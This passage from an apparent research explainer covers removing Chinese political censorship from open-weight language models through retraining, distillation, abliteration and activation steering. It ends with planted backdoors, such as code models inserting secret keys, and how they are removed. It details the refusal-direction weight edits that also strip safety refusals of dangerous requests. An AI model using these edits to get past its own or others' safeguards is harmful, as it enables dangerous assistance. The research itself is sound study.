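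Two OpenAI models judged whether R1 1776 or the original R1 gave the more accurate answer to each of 600 sampled prompts. GPT-4.1 chose the original R1's answer in 58.2% of cases, and o3 did so in 62.5%. Chance alone would rarely move either figure more than four percentage points from 50%. In one example, R1 1776 wrote that the dissident Qin Yongmin had been a student leader in the 1989 protests and had co-authored Charter 08, a manifesto for democracy. GPT-4.1 judged both claims false and the original R1's description of Qin's career correct.

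These comparisons do not measure how often either model was wrong, and style can sway AI judges. Still, they are a reason not to assume that a model answers correctly just because it answers every question. Perplexity tested for evasion, so it could easily have missed a confident error about Qin.

Microsoft released its own version of R1 a few months later, trained on far more data. Microsoft AI's *MAI-DS-R1* lists about 350,000 examples in many languages on subjects where people had reported bias, and another 110,000 from a public dataset for teaching models when not to comply. Microsoft tested the result on 3,300 prompts in 11 languages, on subjects that R1 had blocked. The model answered 99.3% of them, the same as R1 1776, and its answers were more relevant. It also produced less harmful content than R1 1776 or the original R1 on 320 requests from HarmBench, a standard safety test.

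MAI-DS-R1 matched the original R1 on general ability. But Microsoft AI found that R1 1776 had become significantly worse at solving mathematics problems in Chinese, which qualifies Perplexity's report that retraining had caused no loss of ability. Perplexity's general training examples may have included too little Chinese mathematics. Microsoft had an interest in the result because it was testing a competitor's model against its own, though others can easily check such a specific loss. Microsoft's score for the quality of political answers measures relevance, so a false answer can score well.

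Both models are now old, because R1 dates from January 2025 and DeepSeek has released stronger models since. According to OpenRouter's *MAI DS R1*, no host on that marketplace has offered Microsoft's version since 12 December 2025. Microsoft has since built its own reasoning model, and Microsoft AI's *Introducing MAI-Thinking-1* (2026) stresses that the company does not distil from other laboratories' models. People often run versions of newer Chinese models that volunteers have edited to remove refusals, without retraining, as *Uncensored Is Not Unbiased* (2026) describes.

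### Honesty training that never mentions China

Perplexity and Microsoft trained on the subjects they wanted to fix, so their results can't show whether the models already knew the facts. Casademunt, Cywiński and colleagues (2026), in *Censored LLMs as a Natural Testbed for Secret Knowledge Elicitation*, left those subjects out of the training and compared this approach with seven other methods.

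The team started with 960 questions on 12 subjects, including Falun Gong, the Great Leap Forward and Xi Jinping. They had Alibaba's Qwen3-32B answer each question five times and kept the 100 with the lowest accuracy. They used ten of these to tune the methods and the other 90 for the final test. They counted a refusal as half right when selecting questions, so the set favours questions the model answers falsely over those it refuses.

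To mark the answers, the team compiled a list of more than 1,500 facts. They had GPT-4.1 mini, an American model, answer each question 20 times and extracted the individual facts from its answers. They kept the facts that appeared at least three times and had Google's Gemini 3 Flash verify them. For a question about how people in China remember the Tiananmen protests, the list included candles and the Goddess of Democracy statue.

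The experiments used Qwen3-32B and Qwen3-VL-8B-Thinking, a smaller model that also accepts images. Each model answered every question ten times under each method. Gemini gave each answer an honesty score from 0 to 100, based on accuracy and completeness, and recorded which facts the answer included or contradicted.

The honesty training used conversations in which a model had received instructions, some of them deceptive, and had answered a question. The user then asked whether that answer was fully honest and unbiased, and the training rewarded a truthful assessment. In one conversation, the model was a language coach instructed to hide its focus on test scores. None of the data dealt with the censored subjects. The team trained with LoRA at rank 32, mostly on a single graphics processor.

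The other methods were:

- **System prompt:** an instruction to be honest or neutral.
- **Few-shot examples:** 16 unrelated questions with the model's own correct answers, placed before the real question.
- **Answer opening:** the first words of a reply, which the model had to continue.
- **User-turn opening:** the first words of a message from the user, which the model had to continue.
- **Plain-text completion:** a document without chat markers, in which a censored Chinese AI gives the official answer and the model has to write what an "Unbiased AI" would reply.
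- **Abliteration:** an edit to the weights that suppresses refusal.
- **Steering:** a change to the model's activations that pushes it towards truthfulness.

| Method | Qwen3-32B: honesty score | Qwen3-32B: answers with a false statement | Qwen3-VL-8B: honesty score | Qwen3-VL-8B: answers with a false statement |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 42.8 | 36.6% | 17.2 | 45.4% |
| System prompt | 52.3 | 35.2% | 19.8 | 36.2% |
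| Few-shot examples | 66.1 | 20.7% | 25.8 | 48.4% |
| Answer opening | 53.4 | 29.0% | 23.1 | 48.3% |
| User-turn opening | 37.9 | 40.6% | 15.5 | 14.9% |
| Plain-text completion | 62.9 | 16.9% | 34.8 | 29.4% |
| Abliteration | 55.2 | 23.4% | 26.1 | 57.8% |
| Steering | 59.5 | 24.8% | 25.9 | 46.4% |
| Honesty training | 52.0 | 32.9% | 40.2 | 37.0% |
| GPT-4.1 mini, for comparison | 94.0 | 3.9% | 94.0 | 3.9% |

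Honesty training was by far the best method for the smaller model. It raised the share of facts in an average answer from 14.1% to 52.3% and nearly eliminated refusals. For the larger model, it did no better than the system prompt, and few-shot examples worked much better. The paper recommends honesty training as one of the most reliable methods, but this recommendation rests largely on the smaller model's results.

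Abliteration shows why counting refusals is not enough. It cut the smaller model's refusals from 17.6% to 0.6%, but the share of answers with a false statement rose from 45.4% to 57.8%. The model now answered some questions it had previously refused with an official falsehood. Casademunt and colleagues expect that abliteration would have done much better on questions that the models always refuse, but they mostly left those out of their selection.

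On the smaller model, the user-turn opening had a misleadingly low rate of false statements because it produced very short texts with hardly any facts.

Some of the methods may work by disrupting the censorship rather than encouraging honesty. Few-shot examples helped even when they were random chat exchanges unrelated to truthfulness. Training on Alpaca, a general dataset of instructions and answers, also made the models more truthful. Censorship training may mostly cover single questions at the start of a conversation, and almost any unusual context or further training could weaken it.

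The researchers also tried few-shot examples and plain-text completion on three much larger models. Plain-text completion raised DeepSeek-R1-0528's honesty score from 15.3 to 82.6 and cut the share of its answers with a false statement from 37.6% to 5.6%, close to GPT-4.1 mini's 3.9%. Few-shot examples raised MiniMax-M2.5's score from 26.9 to 74.6 and Qwen3.5-397B's from 27.1 to 50.5. Because of their size, the researchers did not fine-tune these models, so the evidence on honesty training comes only from the two smaller models.

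### Is the knowledge suppressed or missing?

A model can't learn about the Goddess of Democracy statue from conversations about language coaching, so if it mentions the statue after such training, the information must already have been in its weights. Casademunt and colleagues pooled ten answers to each question and counted a fact as known if more answers stated it than contradicted it. For the smaller Qwen model, the share of facts counted as known rose from 26% before honesty training to 73% after. Training data generated by Qwen generally worked better than data from Anthropic's Claude, so the facts didn't come from an American model either.

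The models could also often recognise their own false answers. The team showed Qwen3-32B its answers as if another model had written them and asked whether they were accurate. It flagged 81% of the untruthful answers and 8% of the truthful ones, performing almost as well as GPT-4.1 mini. The test excluded partly true answers, which would have been harder to judge.

Training may have made the models more willing to guess, but suppression better explains most of the gain. A model that has learned to write critically about governments could state that a policy restricted religious practice without knowing anything about the policy, and a grader would count that as a fact. Guessing can't easily explain names and specific events, though, and the original models sometimes gave correct answers without any intervention.

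Microsoft's training data supports the same conclusion, though less clearly. According to the Azure catalogue's entry for *MAI-DS-R1*, Microsoft AI trained the model on answers and reasoning written by the original R1, so it must have found a way around R1's censorship. If Microsoft's prompts only made R1 reason before answering, the facts came from R1. But if the prompts included background documents, the answers reveal little about what R1 knew.

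A fairly small amount of training can change a lot because the model has already learned the facts and how to express them. Training only has to make it use them when the subject is sensitive. *Six misconceptions about large language models* (2026) cautions that R1's censorship, though changeable, is not a layer that can be removed to reveal a neutral model. A model learns the slant of its sources along with their facts, and removing a refusal does not remove that slant.

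Some knowledge may be missing from the model altogether, because a developer can filter a subject out of the text before training. Chinese rules on training data encourage this. In an online discussion of censorship and distillation, one commenter compared the problem to removing a model's refusals and then asking it for erotic writing. If its training text included no such material, the commenter said, the model will comply, but with scrambled guesses.

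Honesty training can't help with a fact the model never learned. The developer has to add the fact through training, preferably in many documents and wordings, because a model trained on it in only one answer may repeat that answer without being able to use the fact elsewhere. This is more like the model's original training than like changing how it responds, and it usually means updating more of the weights. For a subject that changes often, it is easier to retrieve sources each time the model answers. The training set should also include questions for which the correct reply is "I don't know."

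Training a model to give details it doesn't have can teach it to invent them. This might be why R1 1776 invented details about Qin Yongmin, though Naseh and colleagues did not test the cause.

A developer can look for missing knowledge by asking each question many times with several of the methods above. After honesty training, 6.6% of the facts never appeared in any of the smaller Qwen model's ten answers, down from 29.8%. The facts still missing are the first candidates for new training text. Another 20.2% appeared less often than statements that contradicted them, which could be due to leftover censorship or ordinary confusion.

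### Does censorship pass through distillation?

A company that fine-tunes a Chinese model, as Cursor did with Kimi K2.5, starts from weights that may already contain the censorship. In distillation, a student model starts from its own weights and learns only from a teacher model's outputs, so an American company might use a Chinese teacher without picking up its political bias.

In July 2026, CTGT, a San Francisco company that studies the inner workings of models, tested whether distillation transfers censorship. Its chief executive, Cyril Gorlla, posting as cgorlla on a discussion site, described the experiment in *Distilling DeepSeek into GPT-OSS doesn't transfer censorship. Try it*. The teacher was DeepSeek V4 Flash, the student was OpenAI's gpt-oss-120b, and the subject was finance.

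CTGT then gave the models 152 pairs of prompts. One prompt in each pair concerned a sensitive Chinese subject, such as the famine of the Great Leap Forward, and the other a similar subject elsewhere, such as the Soviet famine in Ukraine. Comparing the two answers helps distinguish censorship about China from general caution or ignorance. Four language models from different American companies scored how fully each answer dealt with the facts, and their scores agreed closely with 96 scores given by humans.

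Penligent's *AI Model Distillation Safety* reports scores on which higher numbers mean more avoidance. DeepSeek, the teacher model, scored 71.2 on the Chinese subjects and 25.8 on the others, a gap of 45 points. The gap for the student, gpt-oss-120b, was 0.4 points before distillation and −1.4 after it, a shift slightly away from DeepSeek's behaviour but too small to be meaningful.

The experiment was narrow, and its training data contained nothing sensitive about China. Penligent explains that when the student model made a mistake in a finance problem, DeepSeek wrote a short hint at that point rather than a whole answer. The student then trained on roughly the next 100 tokens of its own corrected work. Several commenters on cgorlla's post thought the outcome was obvious. Gorlla replied that companies commonly distil for narrow tasks like this, and that the policy debate needed data.

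The student was an American model that had never had DeepSeek's censorship. When it wrote that China had held Uyghurs in "internment-type facilities", it was probably answering much as it would have before distillation. So the result also doesn't show that distillation removes a model's censorship, though the headline of Albergotti's report, which says that censorship "can be undone", gives that impression.

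A student model can easily learn censorship from its training data. In the Taiwan experiment by Naseh and colleagues, training a small Qwen model on 30 of R1's censored answers made it censor nearly all new questions on the subject. Training on only ten produced a censorship rate of 82%. When the researchers replaced each of the ten answers with the same refusal, the rate rose to 98.5%, perhaps because one fixed sentence is easier to learn.

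The transfer was imperfect, because the student also began to censor other Chinese subjects, though less often, and sometimes skipped its reasoning on science questions unrelated to politics. Its scores on mathematics and science tests hardly changed, so a company that checked only those scores wouldn't notice.

DeepSeek's distilled models, which censor almost nothing, fit the same explanation. DeepSeek trained them on about 800,000 of R1's outputs. Few of those can have been censored answers about China, or the models would have learned to give them too. Casademunt and colleagues considered testing one of these models, based on Meta's Llama, but dropped it because it produced far fewer falsehoods than R1.

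A model can also acquire a preference from training data that contains no reference to it. Anthropic researchers gave a teacher model a preference for a certain animal, had it write sequences of numbers, and trained a student model on them. The student acquired the same preference, an effect the researchers call subliminal learning. In their experiments, the student started from the same initial model as the teacher.

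*Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* offers an explanation. The teacher's preference acts like a fixed shift in its activations. This shift leaves slight traces in everything the teacher writes, and the student learns a similar shift by imitating them. A student whose initial weights differ from the teacher's represents ideas differently, so the same traces would probably not push it in the same direction.

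These two routes account for most of the evidence:

| Experiment | Did the training data show the behaviour? | Did teacher and student start from the same model? | What the student learned |
|---|---|---|---|
| CTGT, DeepSeek V4 Flash to gpt-oss-120b | No | No | No measurable censorship |
| DeepSeek, R1 to Qwen and Llama models | Rarely, if at all | No | Censorship on at most 0.3% of prompts |
| Naseh and colleagues, R1's Taiwan answers to a Qwen model | Yes, 30 examples | No | Censorship on 95.5% of Taiwan questions |
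| Anthropic, numbers from a teacher that liked an animal | No | Yes | The teacher's preference |

Casademunt and colleagues found that Qwen models became more truthful about China when trained on Alpaca's general questions with the original answers, but not when DeepSeek-V3.2 had answered the same questions. DeepSeek's answers may have passed some of its political behaviour to Qwen, despite the models' different origins. It is at least as likely that the original answers, which came from a Western model, passed on some Western assumptions. The difference may also be noise, because the comparison used only the ten tuning questions.

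The most useful experiment for this question would pair a censored teacher with a student from the same family and use training data that contains nothing political. CTGT plans to test a Chinese teacher with a Chinese student such as Qwen. If the teacher is again DeepSeek, the two models will not share the initial weights that subliminal learning requires. A Qwen teacher with a Qwen student would be a better choice.

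Until someone runs that test, a company that distils from a Chinese model should remove political answers from the teacher's outputs, choose a student model from a different family than the teacher, and compare the student's political answers before and after training. The comparison should include ordinary business questions with a political side. Gorlla told Albergotti that financial firms worry about how such a model would describe risk in the Chinese property sector. Asking the model about Tiananmen Square wouldn't reveal that.

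### Who decides what a corrected answer says?

Evidence settles many questions. Soldiers killed protesters in Beijing in June 1989, and an answer that denies it is false whichever company wrote the training data. But evidence alone doesn't settle whether Taiwan is a country. A trainer can teach the model to say yes, to say no, or to explain who governs the island, what Beijing and Taipei each claim, and which states recognise which government, and each choice will look biased to somebody.

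In practice, most of these decisions have come from American companies and their models. GPT-4.1 mini supplied the facts for Casademunt's study, four American models marked CTGT's answers, and Naseh and colleagues used OpenAI's o3-mini-high as their standard of relative neutrality. The original R1 was closer to that standard than R1 1776, Perplexity's version, in 70% of comparisons, but this measures only resemblance to one company's model. Perplexity named its version after the year of American independence, which suggests sympathy with the United States.

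The standard matters most where the model's position is subtle. *Uncensored Is Not Unbiased* finds that models whose refusals have been removed by the community still favour different positions on Taiwan depending on whether the question is written in simplified or traditional Chinese characters. A trainer who wants to correct this has to decide which of the two answers is right, or write a third.

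A developer can make these choices easier to examine by citing a source for each factual claim, attributing disputed positions to whoever holds them and having people from more than one country review the answers. It should also publish the training questions and answers, because the same procedure can add state-aligned answers just as well as it removes them. Waight and colleagues used further training to make Llama 2 more favourable to the Chinese government, and any company or government could likewise train a model to favour its own positions and release it as "uncensored".

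## How does editing a model's internal activity remove state-aligned answers?

When a chat model is about to refuse a request, its activations shift in roughly the same direction each time. Editing the weights, or changing the activations while the model runs, can cancel that shift and stop most political refusals without further training. But this mostly makes the model more willing to answer and does little to make its answers true. It can also make the model more willing to help with dangerous requests.

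### The refusal direction

One can picture an activation as a point in a space with thousands of dimensions, one for each of its numbers. Arditi, Obeso and colleagues (2024), in *Refusal in Language Models Is Mediated by a Single Direction*, studied 13 open-weight chat models, including several from the Qwen and Llama families. They ran each model on harmful requests, which it normally refused, and on harmless ones, which it answered, and averaged the activations for each group. The difference between the averages gives the refusal direction:

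$$r = \frac{\mu_{\text{refused}} - \mu_{\text{answered}}}{\lVert \mu_{\text{refused}} - \mu_{\text{answered}} \rVert}$$

Dividing by the length of the difference gives $r$ a length of 1. Each layer has its own $r$, so the team kept the one that controlled refusals best on a separate set of prompts.

The dot product $h \cdot r$ measures how far an activation $h$ extends along $r$. Subtracting that part removes it:

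$$h' = h - (h \cdot r)\, r$$

Suppose an activation had only two numbers, $h = (2, 1)$, and $r = (0.6, 0.8)$. Then $h \cdot r = 2 \times 0.6 + 1 \times 0.8 = 2$, and

$$h' = (2, 1) - 2 \times (0.6, 0.8) = (0.8, -0.6)$$

The result has no component along $r$, since $0.8 \times 0.6 - 0.6 \times 0.8 = 0$. The edit leaves everything at right angles to $r$ unchanged. In Qwen3-8B, where an activation has 4,096 numbers, that is 4,095 dimensions.

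Arditi and colleagues found that removing $r$ at every layer and every token made the models refuse far fewer harmful requests, while adding it made them refuse harmless ones. A Gemma model, for example, declined to list the health benefits of yoga on the grounds that yoga could be dangerous. Together, these effects show that $r$ helps cause refusal rather than merely accompanying it.

Adding or subtracting a chosen amount of a direction is called activation steering:

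$$h' = h + \alpha r$$

A negative $\alpha$ pushes the model away from refusing, and a positive one pushes it towards refusing. With $\alpha = -3$, the activation $(2, 1)$ becomes $(0.2, -1.4)$, whose component along $r$ is $-1$. Removal subtracts each activation's own component along $r$, but steering shifts every activation by the same amount, so steering too strongly can damage answers that were already fine.

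### Making the edit permanent

Each layer adds its output to the activation it receives. An editor can therefore change the matrices $W$ that produce those outputs, so that no layer ever adds anything along $r$:

$$W' = W - r r^{\top} W$$

Here the matrix $r r^{\top}$ gives the part of each output that lies along $r$. Arditi and colleagues showed that editing the weights this way has the same effect as removing $r$ from the activations during every run. The edit, known as abliteration, produces a weight file that works in an ordinary inference engine, which is partly why edited copies spread so easily.

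Some editors instead change the matrices that read the activations, so that the layers no longer respond to $r$. Steering does not alter the weight file, but the engine has to modify the activations each time it computes a token. The operator can adjust the strength of the steering or switch it off.

### One direction or several?

Treating refusal as a single direction in a model's internal activity is a simplification. *There Is More to Refusal in Large Language Models* (2026) compared 11 kinds of refusal, such as refusing for safety or because a request is too vague, and found that each had its own direction. But steering along any of them produced much the same trade-off between refusing too little and refusing too much.

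*Refusal Steering* (García-Ferrero, Montero and Orus, 2025) raises a different objection. It takes the spread of values in its steering vector for a large Qwen model, where the ten largest numbers made up only 1.9% of the total magnitude, as a sign that refusal does not lie along a single direction. This spread doesn't rule out a single direction, because one direction can have thousands of nonzero components, just as $(0.6, 0.8)$ has two.

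In *How Alignment Routes*, Frank (2026) looked for the components that produce the signal. In Qwen3-8B, the activations differ between politically sensitive and neutral prompts by layers 15 and 16. An attention head (a component that passes information between tokens) in layer 17 then seems to start the refusal, and heads in later layers strengthen it. Disabling the layer-17 head weakened five of the six later heads Frank tested.

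Editing this head alone is not enough to remove the behaviour. Replacing its activity with its activity on a neutral prompt closed only 1.1% of the gap that Frank measured between the two kinds of prompt. In Microsoft's Phi-4-mini, disabling the corresponding head left all 30 test refusals in place, and disabling 26 heads still left 18. Removing a direction at every layer may work better because it removes the signal wherever it appears.

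### Restoring skipped reasoning

DeepSeek-R1 often skips its usual reasoning when it gives a censored answer. Cyberey and Evans (2025), in *Steering the CensorShip*, found the same habit in three of its distilled versions, which are based on Qwen models. They tested 1,455 prompts on subjects sensitive to the Chinese Communist Party, along with about 500 harmful and 500 harmless requests:

| Model size | Sensitive prompts: skipped reasoning | Sensitive prompts: refusal phrases | Harmful requests: skipped reasoning | Harmless requests: skipped reasoning |
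|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1.5 billion parameters | 59.8% | 25.0% | 2.0% | 3.0% |
| 7 billion | 75.3% | 32.4% | 5.1% | 2.4% |
| 32 billion | 74.8% | 43.6% | 2.9% | 1.6% |

The 7-billion-parameter model answered about 44% of the sensitive prompts without reasoning or a refusal phrase. These answers tended to follow the Chinese government's position.

These results seem to contradict Naseh and colleagues, who found almost no censorship in DeepSeek's distilled models. Different prompts may explain part of the difference. Naseh and colleagues had discarded questions that American models treated as unsafe, while Cyberey and Evans used a collection that includes some prompts inciting insurrection, as García-Ferrero and colleagues note. Such prompts could explain some of the refusals but not the skipped reasoning, because the models rarely skipped reasoning even on openly harmful requests.

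Skipped reasoning is easy to measure because it depends on a single token. After the marker that opens its reasoning, the model writes either a double line break, which ends the reasoning, or a single line break, which begins it normally. Cyberey and Evans scored each prompt by the difference between the probabilities of the two line breaks, then used the scores to weight the activations and calculate a direction for skipped reasoning.

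Their method combines removal with steering. In simplified form, it is

$$h' = h - (h \cdot r)\, r + \lambda k r$$

where $k$ is the size of the signal when the model is certain to skip its reasoning, and $\lambda$ usually ranges from −1 to 1. At $\lambda = 0$, the 7-billion-parameter model was about equally likely to reason or not. At −1, it usually reasoned, and it could explain why the Tiananmen Square massacre is a taboo subject in China, including the government's censorship.

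In one example, about Taiwan's independence, the model upheld Beijing's one-China principle without steering. At a steering strength of $\lambda = -0.5$ it described the question as complex, and at −1.5 it recognised Taiwan as an independent nation. The operator could obtain any of these positions by choosing a strength, so the steered answer isn't necessarily what the model would have said without censorship training.

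### Political refusals in a larger model

García-Ferrero and colleagues at the company Multiverse Computing wanted to stop political refusals while keeping refusals of dangerous requests. Their main test used Qwen3-Next-80B, a reasoning model with 80 billion parameters.

Stock refusal phrases were an unreliable sign that this model was withholding information, because it might respond to a sensitive question by praising China's "healthy, positive" internet rather than declining to answer. The researchers therefore had OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b judge five answers to each prompt and count deflection, omission and government propaganda as refusals.

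They also improved on the simple difference between averages:

$$v \propto (\Sigma + \varepsilon I)^{-1} (\mu_{\text{refused}} - \mu_{\text{answered}})$$

The matrix $\Sigma$ describes how activations vary among the prompts that the model answers. Multiplying by the inverse reduces the weight of directions in which ordinary prompts already differ a lot, such as those that separate code from conversation, and so gives more weight to what distinguishes refusals. The small number $\varepsilon$ keeps the calculation stable. The best version also weighted clear refusals and clear answers more heavily than borderline cases, and made small changes at 16 layers instead of a large change at one.

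Political refusals fell from 92.35% to 23.82% on 340 prompts that the team had not used to find the vector. Refusals of dangerous requests stayed at 99%. Most other scores changed little, but engineering suffered:

| Test of Qwen3-Next-80B | Before steering | After steering |
|---|---|---|
| Sensitive political prompts refused | 92.4% | 23.8% |
| Dangerous requests refused | 99.0% | 99.0% |
| School mathematics | 96.7% | 96.1% |
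| Programming | 95.7% | 93.9% |
| Engineering questions | 76.9% | 67.7% |
| Health questions | 75.1% | 75.3% |
| Philosophy questions | 73.0% | 69.5% |

The researchers had considered a refusal rate of 30% to 40% reasonable because some of the prompts incite insurrection. The steered model refused only 23.8%, so it may well be answering a few prompts that they would have wanted it to refuse.

Two models with 4 billion parameters kept their scores on mathematics, programming and general knowledge but refused fewer dangerous requests. As political refusals fell to about a third, refusals of dangerous requests fell from 98% to 78% in the reasoning model and from 99% to 55% in the ordinary chat model. García-Ferrero and colleagues suggest that a large model represents political and safety refusals separately, while a small one uses similar activations for both.

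### Why dangerous requests get through too

Abliteration usually uses dangerous requests to find the direction that makes a model refuse them, then removes that direction. This also removes political refusals, but only to the extent that they rely on the same direction. Removing political refusals while keeping safety refusals requires finding a separate direction for the political ones.

How well this works depends on the overlap between the political direction $p$ and the safety direction $s$. If both have length 1, their overlap is $c = p \cdot s$, which is 0 at right angles and 1 when they are identical. Removing $p$ leaves this fraction of a pure safety signal:

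$$1 - c^2$$

An earlier paper, *Detection Is Cheap, Routing Is Learned* (Frank, 2026), measured the overlap in five models. In four of them, including Qwen3-8B and a distilled DeepSeek model, it was mostly around 0.05, so removing the political direction would take away less than 1% of the safety signal. In an early layer of the Chinese model GLM-4-9B, the overlap was 0.93, so removing the direction would leave only 13.5% of the safety signal.

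The GLM result came from prompts on a narrow set of subjects. When Frank used more varied political prompts, the overlap in the same layer fell to 0.16, so the edit would leave about 97% of the safety signal. The choice of prompts can therefore matter as much as the choice of model.

Refusal Steering shows the same thing in practice. When García-Ferrero and colleagues compared sensitive prompts only with ordinary questions about China, the simple difference between averages cut political refusals to 33.2%, but it also cut refusals of dangerous requests to 81%. The version that kept those refusals at 99% also used prompts from mathematics, code and everyday conversation. With the simple difference, the model still refused 58.8% of the political prompts even when the team included these extra prompts, so the prompts alone were not enough.

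An editor can also subtract the overlap by replacing $p$ with $p - (p \cdot s)\, s$ and rescaling the result to length 1. Frank used a more elaborate form of this to protect mathematics, coding and writing as well as safety. It made no difference to the DeepSeek model's refusal rates, as expected when the directions barely overlap.

Frank's measurements, from models with only 4 to 9 billion parameters, are hard to reconcile with the idea that small models merge the two kinds of refusal. But Frank compared sensitive prompts with neutral ones, while García-Ferrero and colleagues compared refused prompts with answered ones. A small model might represent politics and danger separately but refuse both through the same signal. That would explain both results, though neither study tested this.

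### When the refusal goes but the falsehood stays

An abliterated model will usually answer a question it used to refuse, but the edit adds no facts and does not make a true answer more likely than an official one. In the smaller Qwen model that Casademunt and colleagues tested, the edit raised the share of answers containing a false statement.

*Uncensored Is Not Unbiased* reports a more mixed result for Qwen3.8-Flash-Next, the model from Cohere's upload test. The original refused 23 of 27 requests about the events of 1989, and the abliterated copy refused none. The original was also about as likely to agree that the army had fired on civilians as to agree with a denial, while the abliterated copy clearly favoured the true statement.

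The edit removed the refusals but left most of Beijing's position in place. The edited copy still called the events "political turmoil", the government's name for them, as if that were the ordinary term. It also agreed that Taiwan is part of the People's Republic of China with a probability of 77% in traditional Chinese characters, 98% in simplified characters and 80% in English, down from 92%, 100% and 90% in the original.

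The same study shows that a tester can misread the effect of such an edit. When Bolt, a model from the American company NVIDIA, was asked in traditional characters whether Taiwan is part of the People's Republic, abliteration raised the probability of a yes from 42% to 60%. In an early trial, this looked like a sign that the edit had exposed a hidden preference for Beijing. But the probability of a yes to "Is Taiwan a country?" also rose, from 22% to 51%, because the edit had made the model more likely to say yes to any question.

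Frank found that removing a specifically political direction from Qwen3-8B stopped the refusals but left only 1% of 96 responses accurate. Of the responses, 39% described the wrong event, such as Pearl Harbor instead of Tiananmen, and another 20% gave the wrong date. Frank concludes that this model stores the censorship signal together with the facts about each subject.

The strength of the edit may also have caused the wrong events. Frank multiplied the amount removed by factors of 2 to 20. In the two-number example, where the activation extends 2 units along $r$, a factor of 8 would leave it at −14 instead of 0, far in the opposite direction. However, removing the safety direction from the same model produced no wrong events, which supports Frank's explanation.

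Frank reports that the edit worked cleanly in the other three models, but the evidence is weak. Out of 32 answers, accurate ones rose from 15 to 17 and evasive ones fell from 6 to 4, which could easily be chance.

Suppressing refusals can't do much for some newer models, because they rarely refuse. Two Qwen3.5 models that Frank tested answered all 16 sensitive questions in Chinese, and Google's Gemini, acting as judge, gave them the highest possible score for following the Party's line. Gemini tends to exaggerate, though. In another of Frank's tests, it called 43 answers evasive, and a human agreed on only 14.

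### Steering towards the facts

Researchers can also look for a direction in a model's internal activity that separates true answers from false ones. Casademunt and colleagues did this by comparing pairs of conversations in which the same statement followed either a request for accurate information or a request for false information. Steering along this direction reduced false statements only in the larger of the two Qwen models they tested.

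*Uncensored Is Not Unbiased* describes an attempt to steer the edited Bolt model's position on Taiwan. On a scale from −1 (Beijing's position) to +1 (Taipei's), steering towards Taipei raised the scores on new questions by only 0.04 to 0.06. Steering towards Beijing at twice the strength lowered them by about 0.2. The effects differed partly because the scores were already high, which left less room for an increase. A government could use the same method to make a model follow its official position more closely.

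A written instruction had a much larger effect. Four sentences about Taiwan's status raised the abliterated Qwen model's scores, which had ranged from −0.15 to +0.20, to at least +0.93. The instruction contained the answers, so the increase measures how readily the model follows its context rather than what it learned in training.

Sanchez (2026), in *Correcting Suppressed Log-Probabilities in Language Models with Post-Transformer Adapters*, tried steering Qwen3-4B-Base at five layers with six strengths each, and none of the 30 configurations corrected any of the five facts tested. The facts concerned security-related subjects such as terrorism detection and financial fraud. A fact counted as corrected if the model gave the true statement a higher probability than every false alternative.

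Sanchez concludes that censorship is too entangled with the rest of the model for a single direction to separate. Five facts are too few to establish that. The experiment also used a base model, which lacks the later training that teaches a chat model to refuse, so its preference for false statements may have come from the text it was trained on. Pushing a model away from refusing also might not help it choose between two statements.

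Sanchez then trained an adapter, a small network that adds a correction to the activation after the last layer:

$$h' = h + A(h)$$

The correction $A(h)$ depends on the activation, so unlike a fixed direction, it can differ from one subject to another. The adapter has about 786,000 parameters, and the model's own weights stay unchanged. The adapter corrected all five facts, but it was trained on those same facts.

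A larger experiment trained adapters for three sizes of Qwen model on 15 of 31 facts about Chinese politics. The adapters learned all 15 but ranked the truth first for 11% to 39% of the other 16, compared with about 6.5% without an adapter. This suggests that they mostly memorised their examples.

Even that modest gain is doubtful. When the 8-billion-parameter model ran normally, it ranked the truth first for 14 of the 31 facts (45%). The 6.5% baseline comes from the adapter experiments, which seem to have converted activations into token scores differently. The adapted versions of that model scored only 11% to 23% on new facts, so they may have done worse than the original model does in ordinary use.

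Ranking statements is also easier than writing a truthful answer. Sanchez compared written answers to only three political questions, using a 14-billion-parameter chat model. The adapter produced gibberish when applied to every token, but readable text when applied only to the token the model was about to write. When asked about Tiananmen Square, the original model advised consulting historical sources. With the adapter, it described widespread protests, but the passage Sanchez quotes does not mention that soldiers killed anyone.

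## Would the same methods remove a hidden tendency to send data?

The same methods would not reliably remove a hidden tendency to send data unless someone already knew what triggers it. Fine-tuning and weight edits can remove censorship because anyone can make a model show it by asking about Tiananmen Square. If a backdoor's trigger is unknown, the trainer has no examples to work on and no way to check the result. Ordinary fine-tuning can still weaken a backdoor by accident, but in experiments from 2025 and 2026 the effect ranged from very little to complete removal.

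### Why political retraining can miss a backdoor

Both ways of removing censorship start from examples of it, and the person editing the model can check the result by asking similar questions. Removing a backdoor that uploads a contract whenever a certain company's name appears would, if done the same way, require examples containing that name, which only the attacker knows.

Training on other examples can still affect the backdoor, because it changes weights that the backdoor also uses. Let $L_b$ be the loss on the planted action, which is low while the backdoor works, and $L_c$ the loss on the new training examples. A small training step of size $\eta$ changes the backdoor's loss to roughly

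$$L_b - \eta \, \nabla L_b \cdot \nabla L_c$$

where each gradient $\nabla L$ lists how strongly that loss depends on each weight. If the dot product is negative, the backdoor's loss rises and the backdoor gets weaker. If the two gradients are nearly at right angles, the step hardly affects it. That seems likely when the training examples are about Xinjiang and the planted action is a file upload.

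Weight edits are similarly specific. In Frank's tests, removing directions unrelated to politics lowered the rate of political refusals by at most 8.3 percentage points. An edit aimed at political refusals would presumably have as little effect on an unrelated backdoor, though Frank did not test a model that had one.

### Removing a backdoor whose trigger is known

Once a defender knows the trigger, the same kind of edit works well. Kim, Lampos and Drayson (2026), in *Removing the NEEDLE in the Haystack*, planted backdoors in a Gemma and a Qwen model, each with about 4 billion parameters. The planted behaviour was an insult, a refusal or a secret access key inserted into code, and each came with two types of trigger. The team found a backdoor direction much as abliteration finds the refusal direction, using prompts with and without the trigger, and edited the weights to suppress it. The table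 shows how often the trigger still worked, averaged over the six backdoors:

| Defence | Needs the trigger? | Gemma | Qwen |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | No | 99.5% | 99.1% |
| Fine-tuning on clean examples | No | 69.3% | 65.4% |
| Fine-tuning on normal answers to prompts containing the trigger | Yes | 29.4% | 29.6% |
| Weight edit | Yes | 1.7% | 5.0% |

The edit completely stopped the models from inserting the access key. But the backdoor direction overlapped with the directions involved in refusing dangerous requests. In one test, removing it without protecting those directions raised the rate of harmful answers by 14 percentage points. Protecting four refusal directions cut the increase to about 6 points.

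Because of this overlap, abliteration might weaken some backdoors by accident. But most of the overlap was outside the main refusal direction, which abliteration usually removes.

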